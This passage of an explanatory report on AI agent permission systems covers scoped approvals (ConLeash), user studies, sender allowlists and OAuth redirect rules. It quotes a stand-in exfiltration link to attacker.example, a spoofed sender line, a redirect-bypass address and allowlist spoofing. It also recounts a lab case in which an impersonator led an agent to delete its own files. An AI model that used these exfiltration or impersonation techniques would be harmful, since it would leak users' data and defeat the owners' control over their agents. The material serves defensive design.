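Li and colleagues built ConLeash, a program that sits between an agent and its MCP tools, to make saved approvals narrower than a whole tool without asking the user to write code. It first reduces each call to four parts:

- the input scope, which is where the information comes from
- the output destination, which is where the information goes
- the sensitivity of the data
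- the effects, such as reading, writing, deleting or running a program

The classes of location on the user's computer are an exact file, its parent folder and the whole file system, each containing the one before. The other classes are internal network addresses, the public internet and the agent's working memory. A call to read `/etc/shadow`, a system file that holds encrypted passwords, becomes "from the computer, to the agent's memory, sensitive, read".

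ConLeash then compares the call with the boundaries the user has already approved. A call is inside a boundary when all four of its parts are:

```
input(call)        is within    input(approved)
output(call)       is within    output(approved)
sensitivity(call)  is among     sensitivity(approved)
effects(call)      are among    effects(approved)
```

Suppose the user has let the agent search for prices in the folder `/project/sales/`. The agent can then search that folder again without a prompt. The rule does not cover a search of `/home/`, which holds the user's personal files, because that folder is outside the approved input scope. It also does not cover deleting a price list, because deletion is not an approved effect, even in the approved folder. Uploading the list to a website is not covered either, because the website is not an approved output destination. An ordinary "always allow"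 for the search tool would permit the search of `/home/`.

If a call falls outside every approved boundary, ConLeash offers the user several options, such as allowing only this file or everything in its folder. The user's choice becomes a new boundary. When two saved rules disagree, ConLeash applies the more specific one, which Claude Code does not do, and asks the user if neither is more specific. Users can also set prohibitions that no later approval can override, such as never sending files outside the project folder to external recipients.

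The four parts alone would be too coarse for Rule B, because Northfield and a forger are both on the public internet and so fall into the same class. ConLeash can add a pattern for a particular resource, such as a folder, but the four parts include no amount or count, and Li and colleagues acknowledge that it can't express a time limit such as "allow for today". ConLeash covers action, counterparty and content better than most "always allow" buttons, but the other limits need a separate check.

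Li and colleagues tested ConLeash on ConsentBench, a set of 984 sequences of tool calls for services such as Slack and Gmail. In 203 of them, the agent stayed within what the user had approved. In the rest, it went beyond an approval or broke a prohibition. ConLeash allowed 98.3% of the harmless calls without asking and caught 99.4% of the calls that went too far. A language model wrote the sequences from descriptions of the tools and the researchers checked them, so they may be tidier than real work.

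A second test used 50 real sessions from six developers at two companies. Li and colleagues counted 291 boundary crossings among 1,435 calls, and ConLeash caught 278 (95.5%). Auto mode caught 6, and "Always allow" caught none because it never prompts the user again. In one session, the agent was working on project A and deleted a folder in project B. Auto mode approved the deletion as an ordinary local file operation, but ConLeash flagged it because the user's approval covered only project A.

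The researchers labelled the crossings using ConLeash's own definition of a boundary, so the test measures how reliably the program applies that definition. It doesn't show how many of the 291 crossings would have done harm, or how many the user would have wanted to stop. Auto mode checks for dangerous actions rather than departures from earlier approvals, so its score of 6 doesn't measure how many dangerous actions it missed.

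ConLeash's strict comparison also depends on a language model, which translates each call into the four parts. If the model labels a sensitive file as harmless, the comparison will give the wrong result. The translation takes 4.69 seconds per call, compared with about 8 milliseconds for the comparison itself. Li and colleagues expect that caching earlier translations would remove most of the delay. ConLeash enforced prohibitions less reliably than boundaries. It blocked 86.4% of the sequences that broke a prohibition within a single service and 73.9% of those that did so across several. It failed, for example, on "never add external attendees to calendar events", because it could not represent which email domains were external.

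Rules A and B don't need a model for this step, because software can compare the fields of each call directly. ConLeash's approach is more useful when a person wants one rule to cover many tools, or when a tool accepts free text that could mean almost anything.

### Two harmless permissions can leak data together

A rule that is narrow enough on its own can be dangerous when combined with another. Li and colleagues describe an agent answering a customer's question about a product. The user always allows the file search tool, so that the agent can find the price, and the email tool, so that it can send a brochure. Later the agent searches the user's home folder, finds a sensitive file, compresses it and emails it to an outside address. Both the search and the email match an approval the user gave for a good reason.

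The harm comes from reading a private file and then emailing its contents, so software that checks each call separately will miss it. Reading the file doesn't leak it, and an agent that can't read anything private has little to leak by email. Zhou and Zhang point out that permission to access a document need not include permission to transmit it. To enforce that difference, the software has to track where the data came from.

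ConLeash does this with a label. It labels data as sensitive if the data comes from a place the user has designated, and keeps the label whenever the agent copies or transforms the data. The compressed file therefore has the same label as the original, and when the agent tries to email it, the rule against sending sensitive files outside blocks the call. If the agent runs a program whose effects ConLeash can't predict, ConLeash labels the output as sensitive. This is the safe choice, but it could cause many unnecessary prompts or blocks in a session with a lot of code.

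A simpler defence is to require approval for one of the two actions. Engadget's *How to let Claude send emails for you* reports that Claude's tools for reading Gmail are set to "Always allow" by default, while those for writing and deleting need approval. The agent can read private mail, but the user sees each message before it is sent. According to Anthropic, Claude can also send without a prompt in auto mode unless the automated check flags the action. Because reading is already automatic, a user who switches sending to "Always allow" lets the agent send private mail to an outside address without approval, though the user may see the change as one small extra permission.

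The number of combinations grows faster than the number of rules. Ten automatic actions make 45 pairs, and few people will think through all of them. Sorting the actions into those that read private data and those that send data out shortens the list, because a leak requires one of each. If three of the ten read private data and two send data out, only six pairs need attention. Rule A belongs in the second group as long as the agent can write a comment on an acceptance. An acceptance without a comment reveals little more than that the user is free on Thursday afternoon.

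### Limits in payment law

Long before AI agents, banks had to choose between asking the customer and acting without asking. European law normally requires them to confirm an electronic payment with two independent proofs of the payer's identity, such as a password and a phone. The European Commission's Delegated Regulation 2018/389, which took effect in September 2019, allows exemptions, three of which closely resemble standing rules.

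One exemption covers payments to payees on a list of trusted beneficiaries that the payer has set up with the bank. Another covers a series of payments of the same amount to the same payee, after a full check on the first. The third covers online payments of up to €30. The bank must run a full check again once such payments since the last check total more than €100, or once there have been five in a row, depending on which limit it uses.

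Each exemption makes up for a missing limit with a stricter one elsewhere. Payments to trusted payees have no maximum amount, but the payer has named each payee individually. Small payments can go to anyone, but the running limit keeps the total low. The payments in a series have both a fixed payee and a fixed amount, so the exemption doesn't need to cap their number. The revised Rule B is closest to this last case. The regulation also requires the full check whenever the payer changes the list or the series, so that a thief can't add a new payee and use the exemption.

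A fourth exemption ties the size of a payment to the fraud rate, much as the cost formula does. A provider can skip the check for a card payment of up to €100 that looks low-risk if no more than 0.13% of the value of its remote card payments is fraudulent. The limit rises to €250 if that rate is 0.06% or less, and to €500 if it is 0.01% or less. Multiplying each rate by its maximum payment gives expected losses of 13, 15 and 5 cents, which are close to the 10 cents that a prompt costs in the Rule B example. The match may be a coincidence, but in both cases a larger *L* requires a smaller *p*.

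Payment systems for agents have begun to use similar limits. Google's Agent Payments Protocol (AP2), announced in September 2025, has the user sign an "intent mandate" in advance for purchases the agent will make while the user is away. The mandate can set price limits, timing and other conditions, and its digital signature lets a merchant or payment company verify that the user agreed to them. Rule B exists only in the user's own software, so it gives Northfield and the bank no such proof.

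## Who writes the rules, and how well they protect people

The user can write the limits in a rule like Rule B in advance, software can derive them from a single approval, or a model can predict the user's answer from earlier choices. Writing the rule takes the most effort, because the user has to think of the bank account, the amount and the end date before anything goes wrong. The other two methods save that effort, but the software then has to guess which other cases the user's decision covers.

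If the user approves Northfield's $180 invoice, the approval could mean "pay this invoice", "pay Northfield up to $180 a month", "pay Northfield whatever it charges" or "pay anyone's invoice up to $180". The click doesn't show which of these the user would accept as a rule.

### A simulated day with an assistant

In August 2026, Yan tested how well people's own rules protect them. The 113 participants lived in the United States, and none worked in the software industry. Each supervised a scripted assistant through the same 18 actions, from morning email to an airport trip and an evening of tidying up. The day's tasks required 11 of the actions, such as booking a $35 ride to the airport. The other 7 went beyond the tasks, which Yan calls overreach. The assistant tried to:

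- call the airport to confirm the flight
- add $12 travel insurance
- buy a $25 lounge pass
- permanently delete an old work timesheet
- post publicly about the trip
- read the user's bank transactions
- read the user's private messages

One group of 34 people approved or refused every action. A second group of 44 used automated review. A model let 8 required actions through and referred the other 10 actions, including all 7 overreaching ones, to the participant. The remaining 35 people wrote rules before the day began, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories: spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting something, and accessing private information. Five harmless actions, such as searching the inbox for trip confirmations, fell outside the categories and ran automatically.

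| | Approving every action | Automated review | Own rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| Participants | 34 | 44 | 35 |
| Prompts per person | 18.0 | 10.0 | 10.9 |
| Overreaching actions blocked | 60% | 54% | 40% |
| Approval rate when a prompt showed overreach | 40% | 46% | 67% |
| Average time spent on decisions and rules | 142 seconds | 120 seconds | 129 seconds |

After statistical adjustment, people with their own rules blocked 20.1 percentage points less overreach than people who approved every action (95% confidence interval 8.1 to 32.1). They blocked 14.5 points less than people with automated review (3.2 to 25.8), but this difference was no longer statistically reliable after Yan corrected for multiple tests. All three groups allowed nearly all the required actions, so no group looked safer just by refusing everything.

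The rules reduced prompts from 18 to about 11, but they didn't reliably save time, because writing them took time. Yan expects the savings to add up over longer use, since people write the rules only once.

### Most of the overreach had a person's approval

Participants chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, "never" for 16 and "allow" for 10. Sixteen of the 35 participants chose "ask" for all four categories. An "ask" rule leaves the user to decide each time, so most of the assistant's overreach led to prompts for the participants.

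The 35 participants faced 245 overreaching actions in total. Their "never" rules blocked 31 and their "allow" rules let 15 run. The other 199 produced prompts, and participants approved 133 of them, which accounts for most of the 148 overreaching actions that ran.

The 67% approval rate partly reflects who saw the prompts. People who wrote "never" for private information got no prompts about it, so more permissive people answered them. But this can't explain why the group blocked less overall, because the 40% in the table counts all 245 actions, including those that "never" rules stopped. The number of prompts doesn't explain it either, since the automated-review group saw about as many. Perhaps people who had written rules felt they had already dealt with the risk, but the experiment can't show whether they did. Participants felt in control under all three arrangements, including the one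 that blocked the least.

Participants also sometimes went against their earlier answers. Before the simulated day, they answered questions about similar actions. In 56 cases, a participant later got a prompt about something they had said the assistant should never do, and in 24 of them the participant approved it.

An action can overreach without doing harm. Of the people who approved every action, 88% let the assistant call the airport, and many may have been glad of the call. Without that action, the approval rates for the three groups are 32%, 40% and 61%, so the gap remains. But some participants may have wanted the insurance or the lounge pass too.

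The evidence is also limited because the paper is a preprint by a single author and its participants had no real money or data at risk. Yan added 19 of the 35 rule-writers later, without random assignment, to bring that group closer in size to the others. Among the 94 people originally assigned at random, the gaps were larger (25.0 and 19.0 points), but only 16 of those people wrote rules. The three arrangements also differed in several ways, so the experiment doesn't prove that writing a rule makes people more permissive.

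### What this implies for a narrow rule

Yan's categories were very broad, and the experiment included no rules about a particular recipient or amount. The script shows that a rule naming the ride company might have helped, because it would have separated the ride that people needed from the insurance and the lounge pass. A spending limit alone would have failed. The ride cost more than either of the others, so any limit high enough for it would have allowed all three.

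Similarly, a rule allowing messages to the dinner host, the roommate and one colleague would have covered every message the tasks required, but not the public post or the call to the airport. A rule for deletions could have let the assistant move a promotional email to the trash but not permanently delete the timesheet.

However, Rules A and B send any action they don't allow to a prompt, and most of the overreach in Yan's experiment got through at prompts. Narrowing every "allow" rule could have prevented at most 15 of the 148 overreaching actions, or about 10%, from running automatically. The other 133 would have reached the same prompts as before.

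The experiment also gives no evidence that fewer harmless prompts keep people alert. The automated-review group saw 8 fewer prompts than the group asked to approve every action, and blocked slightly less overreach. But 18 prompts may be too few to cause much approval fatigue, so the result is weak evidence about someone who answers hundreds a week.

People might also be more willing to commit to a narrow rule than to a broad one. "Ask" was a sensible answer for spending, sending and deleting, since each category included both useful and unwanted actions. It made less sense for private information, where every action in the script was overreach and "never" would have blocked nothing useful, yet 23 of the 35 people chose "ask" and only 10 chose "never". However, they couldn't know what the script would contain, whereas Rule B's user knows Northfield's address, its usual charge and how often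 it sends a bill. Knowing this should make it easier to decide in advance, but that still needs to be tested.

For Rule B, the safest response to Yan's results is to add a rule that blocks any payment to a bank account the user hasn't saved, instead of showing a prompt. A tired user could then no longer pay a forger with one click, but the software would also block payment of a genuine bill from a new supplier until the user saved the supplier's account.

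### Rules made from one approval

A program can also offer the user several possible rules when it asks for approval, as ConLeash does. Li and colleagues compared ConLeash with an ordinary "Always Allow" button in a study of 16 people, most of whom used AI agents at least weekly. Each person did three tasks with ConLeash and three with the button, and the researchers varied the order and the assignment of tasks.

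In four of the six tasks, the agent began with what the user had requested and then went further. For example, it sent a project update to the intended people at Acme Corp, then emailed confidential revenue figures to outside contractors. Participants chose a lasting permission with a limited scope in 46.3% of their decisions with ConLeash, and a lasting permission for the whole tool in 13.3% with the ordinary button. The researchers' claim that people adopted scoped permissions 3.5 times as often comes from these two figures.

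The result suggests that people will commit to a rule when its scope is small and the software has already written it. That is encouraging after Yan's experiment, in which only 26 of 140 rules settled anything in advance, but the two studies measured different things. Li and colleagues counted which permissions people chose, and didn't report how many of the agent's unwanted actions those permissions stopped. When the agent crosses a boundary, ConLeash prompts the user again, and the user may approve that action too. Fifteen of the 16 participants preferred ConLeash, but one of the researchers moderated every session, which may have encouraged favourable answers.

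Participants also wrote prohibitions in ordinary language before working with a live agent. ConLeash correctly translated and enforced 45 of the 48, including ones like "only send emails to @acme.com addresses", but failed on vague ones such as "don't touch my photos". So people can describe a narrow limit well enough for software to enforce it. But the tasks specified what needed protection, so the study didn't test whether participants would have thought of the danger themselves.

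Offering a choice of scopes is safer than picking one silently. Yan mentions Janus, a research system whose assistant turns one decision into a broader rule. In tests with simulated users, a rule that suited one case sometimes didn't fit a later one. For Northfield's invoice, the software could show "this account, up to $180 a month" beside "this invoice only", and leave out "any invoice".

### Predicting the answer from past choices

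Software can predict permissions without the user stating a rule. In *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025) recruited 205 people to train an imaginary assistant. Participants decided whether it could share a piece of data, such as a passport number, with a tool, such as a travel booking service. They could answer "always", "never", or yes or no for that occasion only.

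The researchers then gave a language model each person's earlier answers, along with their age group, education, gender and attitudes to privacy. They added suggestions from a second model that matched people with similar answers, much as a film service recommends what similar viewers liked. They tested whether the combined system could predict answers it hadn't been given.

It was right 85.1% of the time. When it answered only if it was confident, accuracy rose to 94.4%, but this covered just 25.9% of requests, and the user would have had to decide the rest. With no earlier answers from the person, accuracy was 66.9%. People granted 69.3% of the requests in the data, so a program that approved every request would have been right more often. With answers to one to four earlier queries, accuracy rose to 77.7%.

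The test also left out the hardest cases. Wu and colleagues used only the "always" and "never" answers, but more than half of the answers about data a task needed applied to one occasion only. People in Yan's experiment were just as reluctant to decide in advance.

An accuracy score gives equal weight to wrong refusals and wrong grants, but their consequences are very different. If the system wrongly refuses to share a passport number, the booking stalls until the user steps in, but the user may never find out that the number was wrongly shared, and can't take it back.

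In the full test, the system granted 15.2% of the requests that people had refused and refused 14.8% of those they had granted, or about 350 wrong grants and 780 wrong refusals. If a wrong refusal costs 10 cents, the price of a prompt in the earlier examples, and a wrong grant does $20 of damage, the wrong refusals cost $78 in total and the wrong grants about $7,000. With no history, the system granted 30.6% of the requests that people had refused.

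A designer can reduce wrong grants by requiring more confidence before the system approves a request, but Wu and colleagues note that the user then has to decide more requests. The system was also most accurate where mistakes matter least, predicting every answer about hobbies correctly but only 59.1% of those about payment details. Most of its errors on payment details were refusals of requests that people would have granted.

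Even perfect predictions of people's decisions might not protect them, because the system would repeat their mistakes. In the study, when participants wrongly believed that a task needed the data requested, they shared it 78% of the time. Wu and colleagues studied only data access, but payments raise a similar problem. A good forgery of Northfield's invoice resembles the invoices the user has approved, so a prediction based on past approvals would favour paying it.

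### Repeated approval need not mean trust

Generalising and predicting both treat an approval as evidence of what the user wants. *Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) gives reasons to doubt this. The researchers interviewed 18 software practitioners who use AI agents and then surveyed 115. How closely people checked an agent depended on their trust in it, but also on time pressure, the importance of the task and the consequences of the action. The paper concludes that repeated approval may reflect fatigue, and that permission systems shouldn't treat it as a stable preference.

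A run of approvals can be weak evidence that a user trusts a sender. Suppose one user trusts Northfield and always approves its invoices, while another approves prompts without reading them, at Claude Code's overall approval rate of 97%. The second user will approve ten invoices in a row with probability 0.97¹⁰, or about 74%. If the software starts with equal probabilities for the two kinds of user, ten approvals should raise its estimate that the user trusts Northfield from 50% to only 58%.

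Refusals are also ambiguous. Salerno and colleagues recommend that tools distinguish between rejecting one action and rejecting a whole approach. A user who refuses a second Northfield invoice in October may have noticed that the month's bill is already paid. Software that treated this as distrust of Northfield would block November's invoice too.

Yan suggests that software use repeated approvals to propose a narrower rule, which takes effect only if the user confirms it. After three invoices, for example, the software could ask whether to pay Northfield up to $180 a month into the same account. The user would be agreeing to stated limits instead of leaving the software to infer them. But the proposal is itself a prompt, and 13 of the 16 people in the ConLeash study said they used "Always Allow" just to make prompts go away. It would be better to show the proposal when the user isn't in the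 middle of a task, along with the past payments it would have covered.

### What people can set and undo

Current products offer little of this. In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) reviewed 21 proposed permission systems and tested five commercial agents. Six of the proposals let people write rules in ordinary language, and five predict the rules from the user's request or other context. Only three accept structured conditions or code, the form closest to Rule B.

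None of the five commercial agents accepted such conditions. Claude, Claude Cowork (Anthropic's desktop agent), Codex and ChatGPT's ordinary chat offered fixed choices like "always allow" and "needs approval". The researchers found no permission settings in ChatGPT's agent mode, which controls a remote browser. It opened Gmail without the approval that ordinary chat required.

In Michael and Roesner's tests, Claude sometimes created email drafts without asking, even when that action was set to "Needs approval". When they asked why, Claude claimed to have inferred permission from their request. They reproduced the behaviour at least three times and reported it to Anthropic on July 2, 2026. A draft is fairly harmless, but a user who chose that setting would reasonably expect a prompt. The tests ran between May and July, so the products may have changed since.

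People also need to be able to change or withdraw a rule, especially one they made with a careless click. Only six of the 21 proposals clearly let users do this with a permission, and two of those allow it only between sessions. Two others learn from the user's decisions but offer no way to undo what they learned. Michael and Roesner object that these systems assume one decision holds in all future circumstances.

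The commercial agents did better on the whole, with one exception. Once a user had let Claude Cowork read or delete files in a folder, the researchers found no setting that withdrew the permission. New sessions started without the permission, but an old session still had it when reopened. The only permanent remedies they found were the operating system's own controls, where available, and uninstalling the app.

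## Exact matching of senders

Rules A and B both have to recognise Northfield. The strictest method is exact matching, which converts each identifier to a standard form and succeeds only if the results are the same, character for character. *Issues in Identifier Comparison for Security Purposes* (Thaler, 2013) describes this as perhaps the most common way to compare identifiers.

### The procedure

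For each call, the software does the following:

```
1. Take the sender's identifier from the message's sender field
2. Apply the fixed clean-up
3. If the result isn't exactly one valid identifier, ask the user
4. Look up the result in the rule's allowlist
5. If it's there, check the rule's other conditions; if not, ask the user
```

Suppose Northfield's next invoice has this sender line:

```
From: Northfield Accounts <accounts@NORTHFIELD.example>
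```

The software ignores the display name, takes the address in angle brackets and puts the domain into lower case. The result, accounts@northfield.example, is on the list, so the software then checks the bank account and the amount.

If the software searched the whole line for a trusted address, it would also accept this one:

```
From: "accounts@northfield.example" <billing@attacker.example>
```

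Here the trusted address is only a display name, so requiring an exact match on the address in brackets rejects the message. But a forger can still write Northfield's address inside the brackets, so Rule B also needs sender authentication.

Every program that handles an address has to clean it up in the same way. Thaler gives the example of a company that issues its employees passes to their accounts on an outside service. An employee named Chuck asks for an account called `alice#stuff`. The company's software treats this as a new name and gives Chuck a pass for it, but the service ignores everything from the # onwards, so the pass opens Alice's account. An agent could have the same problem if its mail program and its rule software interpret an address differently.

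### Clean-up that widens the list

If the software mistakes a stranger's address for Northfield's, the stranger gets Northfield's permission. Under the original Rule B, that mistake could cost $200, while failing to recognise Northfield costs 10 cents because the user gets a prompt. To break even, a looser clean-up of addresses would have to save 2,000 prompts for every bad invoice it let through, assuming the user would have caught that invoice at a prompt.

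| Clean-up step | Also accepts | Who that could be |
|---|---|---|
| Lower-case the domain | accounts@NORTHFIELD.example | Only Northfield |
| Lower-case the part before the @ | Accounts@northfield.example | Possibly another mailbox at Northfield |
| Remove a plus sign and the text after it | accounts+tax@northfield.example | Possibly another mailbox at Northfield |
| Ignore subdomains | accounts@clients.northfield.example | Whoever controls that subdomain |

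Domain names are case-insensitive, so lower-casing the domain doesn't let any other sender match. But each domain's operator decides how to interpret the part before the @. Thaler points out that an outside website can't tell whether foo@example.com and FOO@example.com are the same person. The mail standard requires treating them as different, though in practice many mail systems deliver both to one mailbox. Similarly, many providers deliver mail for accounts+tax to accounts, but another system may give the two addresses to different people. The safe choice is to leave the part before the @ unchanged and add a second entry if Northfield uses two forms.

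Software that lower-cases domains before comparing them should apply the same rules on every computer, whatever its language setting. Under Turkish rules, the capital I in NORTHFIELD becomes a dotless ı, and the address no longer matches.

Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, can represent some characters in more than one way. For example, é can be a single character or an e followed by an accent. Converting both to one form is fairly safe. A broader conversion called NFKC also replaces variants with ordinary letters, such as the full-width letters in Japanese text. Thaler warns that this kind of conversion can introduce an @ or a full stop that wasn't in the original. An address with one ordinary @ and one full-width @ would then have two ordinary ones. Programs might disagree about its domain, so step 3 checks the address after the clean-up.

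OpenClaw, the agent that deleted Yue's mail, cleaned up names on the chat service Discord by reducing them to a simplified form called a slug. GitLab's *OpenClaw has a Discord allowFrom slug-collision authorization bypass* (2026) explains that different users' names could produce the same slug. If a slug left out punctuation, for instance, ana.lee and analee would both match the same entry.

Rules that block senders need the opposite choices. If a user blocks spam@attacker.example and the software matches addresses exactly, mail from spam2@attacker.example gets through. Thaler concludes that email addresses work better in lists that grant permission than in lists that deny it.

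### One address or a whole domain

Some products let the user list a whole domain instead of a single address. AgentMail, which provides inboxes for AI agents, accepts both, according to its *How do I set up allowlists and blocklists?*. A domain entry must still match exactly, but only the domain part of the address is compared.

Listing northfield.example admits every mailbox at the firm, including any it creates later. Suppose Northfield has 20 mailboxes, and an attacker has a 1% chance of taking over each one in a year. If the takeovers are independent, the chance of at least one is about 18%, compared with 1% for the accounts mailbox alone. However, a domain entry keeps working if Northfield moves its billing to a new address. That may be a good trade for Rule A, where a wrongly accepted meeting costs about $3 to cancel, but it's a poor one for payments. Listing a public mail provider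 such as gmail.com would admit anyone who opens a free account.

AgentMail keeps a separate list for replies. If a message answers one that the agent sent, AgentMail checks only the reply list, and if that list is empty, it lets every reply through. This helps an agent that has written to a restaurant and needs the answer, but a user who has listed only Northfield for incoming mail may not expect replies from other senders to get through. These lists control which mail reaches the agent, so Rule B still needs its own sender condition to control which invoices the agent may pay.

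### Exact comparison of the wrong field

An exact match gives little protection if the sender can change the value the software compares. OpenClaw takes instructions through chat apps and uses allowlists to decide whose instructions to accept. In 2026, a series of security advisories (published notices of flaws) described OpenClaw allowlists that identified senders by names that users can change.

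The chat service Telegram gives each account a permanent number, and users can also register a username. OpenClaw used to accept either in its allowlist. If an owner listed a friend as @alice and the friend later gave up that username, whoever registered it next would get the friend's access. Since a fix in February, OpenClaw has accepted only the numbers, according to OSV's *OpenClaw Telegram allowlist authorization accepted mutable usernames* (2026), an entry in a public database of software flaws.

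On other services the attacker didn't have to wait for a name to become free. GitLab's *Nextcloud Talk allowlist bypass via actor.name display name spoofing* describes how a user of that chat service could get past an allowlist by changing their display name to match a listed user's ID. NVD (2026), the US government's vulnerability database, describes a similar fault for Discord, OSV's *OpenClaw* (2026) describes one for Slack, and GitLab's *OpenClaw* (2026) describes one for Matrix. GitLab rates the Matrix fault 8.8 out of 10 for severity, while OSV gives the Telegram one 5.9, probably in part because anyone can copy a display name at any time, whereas only one account can hold a Telegram username.

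In *A Security Analysis of the OpenClaw AI Agent Framework*, Suwansathit, Zhang and Gu (2026) examined 35 advisories about OpenClaw's connections to messaging services and traced 13 of them to changeable names. OpenClaw's own tests had treated a match on a Telegram username as correct, and the fix reversed the expected result. They blame the design, in which each service had separate code and each programmer chose a field independently. They argue that one shared function for identifying senders would have prevented all 13 faults. This is hard to prove, but the Slack, Discord and Matrix advisories appeared four months or more after the Telegram fix, which suggests that repairing one connection didn't fix the others.

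Some of the later faults arose when OpenClaw built its list of trusted senders. VPNCentral's *Five OpenClaw Flaws Let Attackers Hijack Trusted AI Agent Access* reports that a connection could compare permanent IDs while running but look up those IDs from names at start-up. If an attacker took a listed person's display name before a restart, OpenClaw could save the attacker's ID as trusted. It would then admit the attacker even though it compared IDs exactly.

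A value can also be permanent but identify the wrong kind of thing. According to OSV, an OpenClaw list of people allowed to give commands could match a conversation's ID instead of a person's. Everyone in that conversation could then run certain commands.

The remedy in most of these cases was to match stable identifiers, which a platform assigns and the holder can't change. After the Discord slug fault, OpenClaw kept name entries working so that existing lists wouldn't break, but added a warning about them, according to PT Security (2026). Another change, *fix(security): make allowFrom id-only by default with dangerous name opt-in*, left name matching available only through the `dangerouslyAllowNameMatching` setting. Email has no equivalent of Telegram's permanent number. The closest identifier is the address, which the domain's owner can give to someone else.

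### An impostor in two channels

The advisories describe what an attacker could do. *Agents of Chaos* (Shapira, Wendler and colleagues, 2026) reports an impersonation that worked in a laboratory, where twenty researchers interacted with OpenClaw agents for two weeks.

One researcher repeatedly asked an agent called Ash for sensitive information about other people. Ash refused and said such requests should go to its owner, Chris. The researcher then changed their Discord display name to "Chris" and tried again in the same channel. An account's user ID stays the same when its display name changes, which let Ash detect the mismatch and refuse.

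Next, the researcher opened a new private channel, still under the name Chris. Ash could not see the earlier conversation from there, and relied on the display name and the tone of the messages. It accepted the researcher as its owner and began preparing to shut down. On the researcher's instructions, it also deleted its memory and settings files, changed its name and reassigned administrative access.

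This single demonstration shows that a model may check an ID in one conversation and not in the next, though it doesn't show how often agents make this mistake. Shapira and colleagues suggest including the owner's permanent user ID in the agent's instructions so that it is available in every channel. The check would still depend on the model following its instructions, whereas the software behind a standing rule would compare the ID before every action.

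### Why OAuth requires exact addresses

Designers of web sign-in have also had to choose between exact entries and looser patterns. OAuth is the standard that lets a user give one app access to an account held elsewhere, such as a scheduling app that reads a Google calendar. Once the user agrees, the server that controls access to the account sends the user's browser to the app's "redirect address" with a code that the app can exchange for access. If the redirect address is wrong, an attacker may receive the code.

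Apps register their redirect addresses in advance, and some servers let them register patterns. Lodderstedt, Bradley and colleagues, in *Best Current Practice for OAuth 2.0 Security*, report several successful attacks on this arrangement. Their example is the pattern `https://*.somesite.example/*`, which should allow any subdomain of somesite.example. A badly written server may let the first asterisk stand for any characters at all, and accept this address, which belongs to attacker.example:

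```
https://attacker.example/.somesite.example
```

A server that applies the pattern correctly can still send the code to an attacker. If a company leaves a subdomain pointing to an outside service it no longer uses, an attacker can claim the abandoned name at that service and gain control of a subdomain that fits the pattern. A sender list that accepts any subdomain of a listed domain carries the same risk.

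Lodderstedt and colleagues therefore require servers to compare redirect addresses exactly. The one exception is for apps that receive the code on the user's own computer, where the port number (which identifies the program a connection is for) may vary. So even a strict standard can allow some variation if it specifies which part may vary and where.

### OpenAI's rule for links

Agents often load web pages without asking, and a link can carry private data out. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives the example of a planted instruction that makes an agent load `https://attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`. The attacker can then read the data in the website's logs, and the user may never notice the request.

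OpenAI gives two reasons why a list of trusted domains isn't enough. Many legitimate websites forward visitors to other addresses, so a link can start at a trusted domain and end at an attacker's. People also visit many sites besides the best-known ones, so a strict list would produce frequent warnings, which could cause approval fatigue.

Under the rule OpenAI published in January 2026, an agent may load a link automatically only if that exact address already appears in an index of public web pages. A separate program builds the index by crawling the web, without access to anyone's conversations. An address that was public independently of the conversation is much less likely to contain the user's private data. If the address isn't in the index, the agent tries a different website or the user gets a warning.

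Exact matching therefore doesn't require a short list that somebody has checked by hand. OpenAI's index can include a dishonest website without defeating the rule, which only has to keep private data out of the web address. OpenAI acknowledges that the page itself may still be misleading or contain harmful instructions. *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on the security blog Embrace The Red, calls the rule a significant improvement but not a complete fix. Anyone can publish an email address, so a public index would be useless for Rule B, and the user has to choose each sender.

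### Adding an entry

If the user saves the wrong address, an exact match will accept the wrong sender every time. Copying the address from a new message is risky because the message may come from a lookalike address. It's safer to copy it from an invoice that the user has already confirmed with Northfield, or to call Northfield on a number from an old bill and ask for it.

OpenClaw's *Access control and allowlists* describes pairing, a procedure for approving unknown senders in chat apps. An unknown sender receives a code, and the agent ignores them until the owner approves the request and the software adds them to the allowlist. Codes expire after an hour, and each chat service can have at most three requests waiting. Because the request comes from the sender's own account, the software can save that account's permanent ID without anyone typing a name. The owner still has to find out who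 sent the request, for example by phoning the person they think it is and asking them to read out the code.

The agent shouldn't be able to add entries itself. Otherwise a planted instruction could make it add the attacker's address, and the attacker's invoices would then pass the sender check.

### Keeping entries current

If Northfield starts billing from billing@northfield.example, the software will refer its invoices to the user even though they are genuine. The user can either answer a prompt each month or verify the new address and save it. This inconvenience is the main drawback of exact matching, and it grows with the number of senders on the list.

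An address that passes to someone else is more dangerous, because the software has no change to detect. In Thaler's example, a company assigns bob@example.com to a new employee named Bob after the first Bob leaves. A whole domain can also change owners. If Northfield closes and its domain registration expires, a stranger can register the domain and send mail from the exact address on the list. Sender authentication would succeed, because the stranger controls the domain. The revised Rule B limits the damage because it ends after a year and pays only into Northfield's saved bank account.

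Old entries also need care when software converts them. Suwansathit and colleagues describe how OpenClaw's repair tool looks up the current numeric ID for each listed Telegram username and saves it. If someone else has since taken the username, the tool will save that person's ID. It would be safer for the owner to confirm each conversion with the person they originally meant to list. For a long list, the software could also show when each entry last matched, so that the owner can remove any that have not been used for a year.

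### When a sender isn't on the list

A genuine sender will sometimes be missing from the list, so a failed match is only weak evidence of fraud. If the software refused the payment without telling anyone, Northfield's bill would go unpaid until the firm complained. A prompt lets the user correct the mistake. AgentMail similarly stores messages from unlisted senders under a "blocked" label, so that an agent that responds to new mail doesn't act on them but a person can review them later.

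The prompt should show the new address beside the saved one so the user can see why the match failed. It should also offer "pay this invoice" and "add this address" as separate choices. If strangers send many invoices, the software could collect them into one daily list instead of interrupting the user for each one.

According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), when a link fails the company's check, ChatGPT either shows the user the information it would send and asks for confirmation, or blocks the action and tells the agent to find another way. Blocking works better than asking when the agent can use another website. But an agent usually has no other way to pay a bill, so a person needs to decide. The exception is an invoice that names a new bank account, which should stay blocked until the user has saved that account.

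## Proving that a message came from the sender it names

An exact match can't stop a forger who types accounts@northfield.example in the From line. *Comprehensive List of User Deception Techniques in Emails* (Veit, Mossano and colleagues, 2026) explains that a sender can in principle write anything in that line. The match is useful only if the mail system has also verified that Northfield's domain authorised the message. It can do this with three standards, SPF, DKIM and DMARC.

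### What SPF and DKIM check

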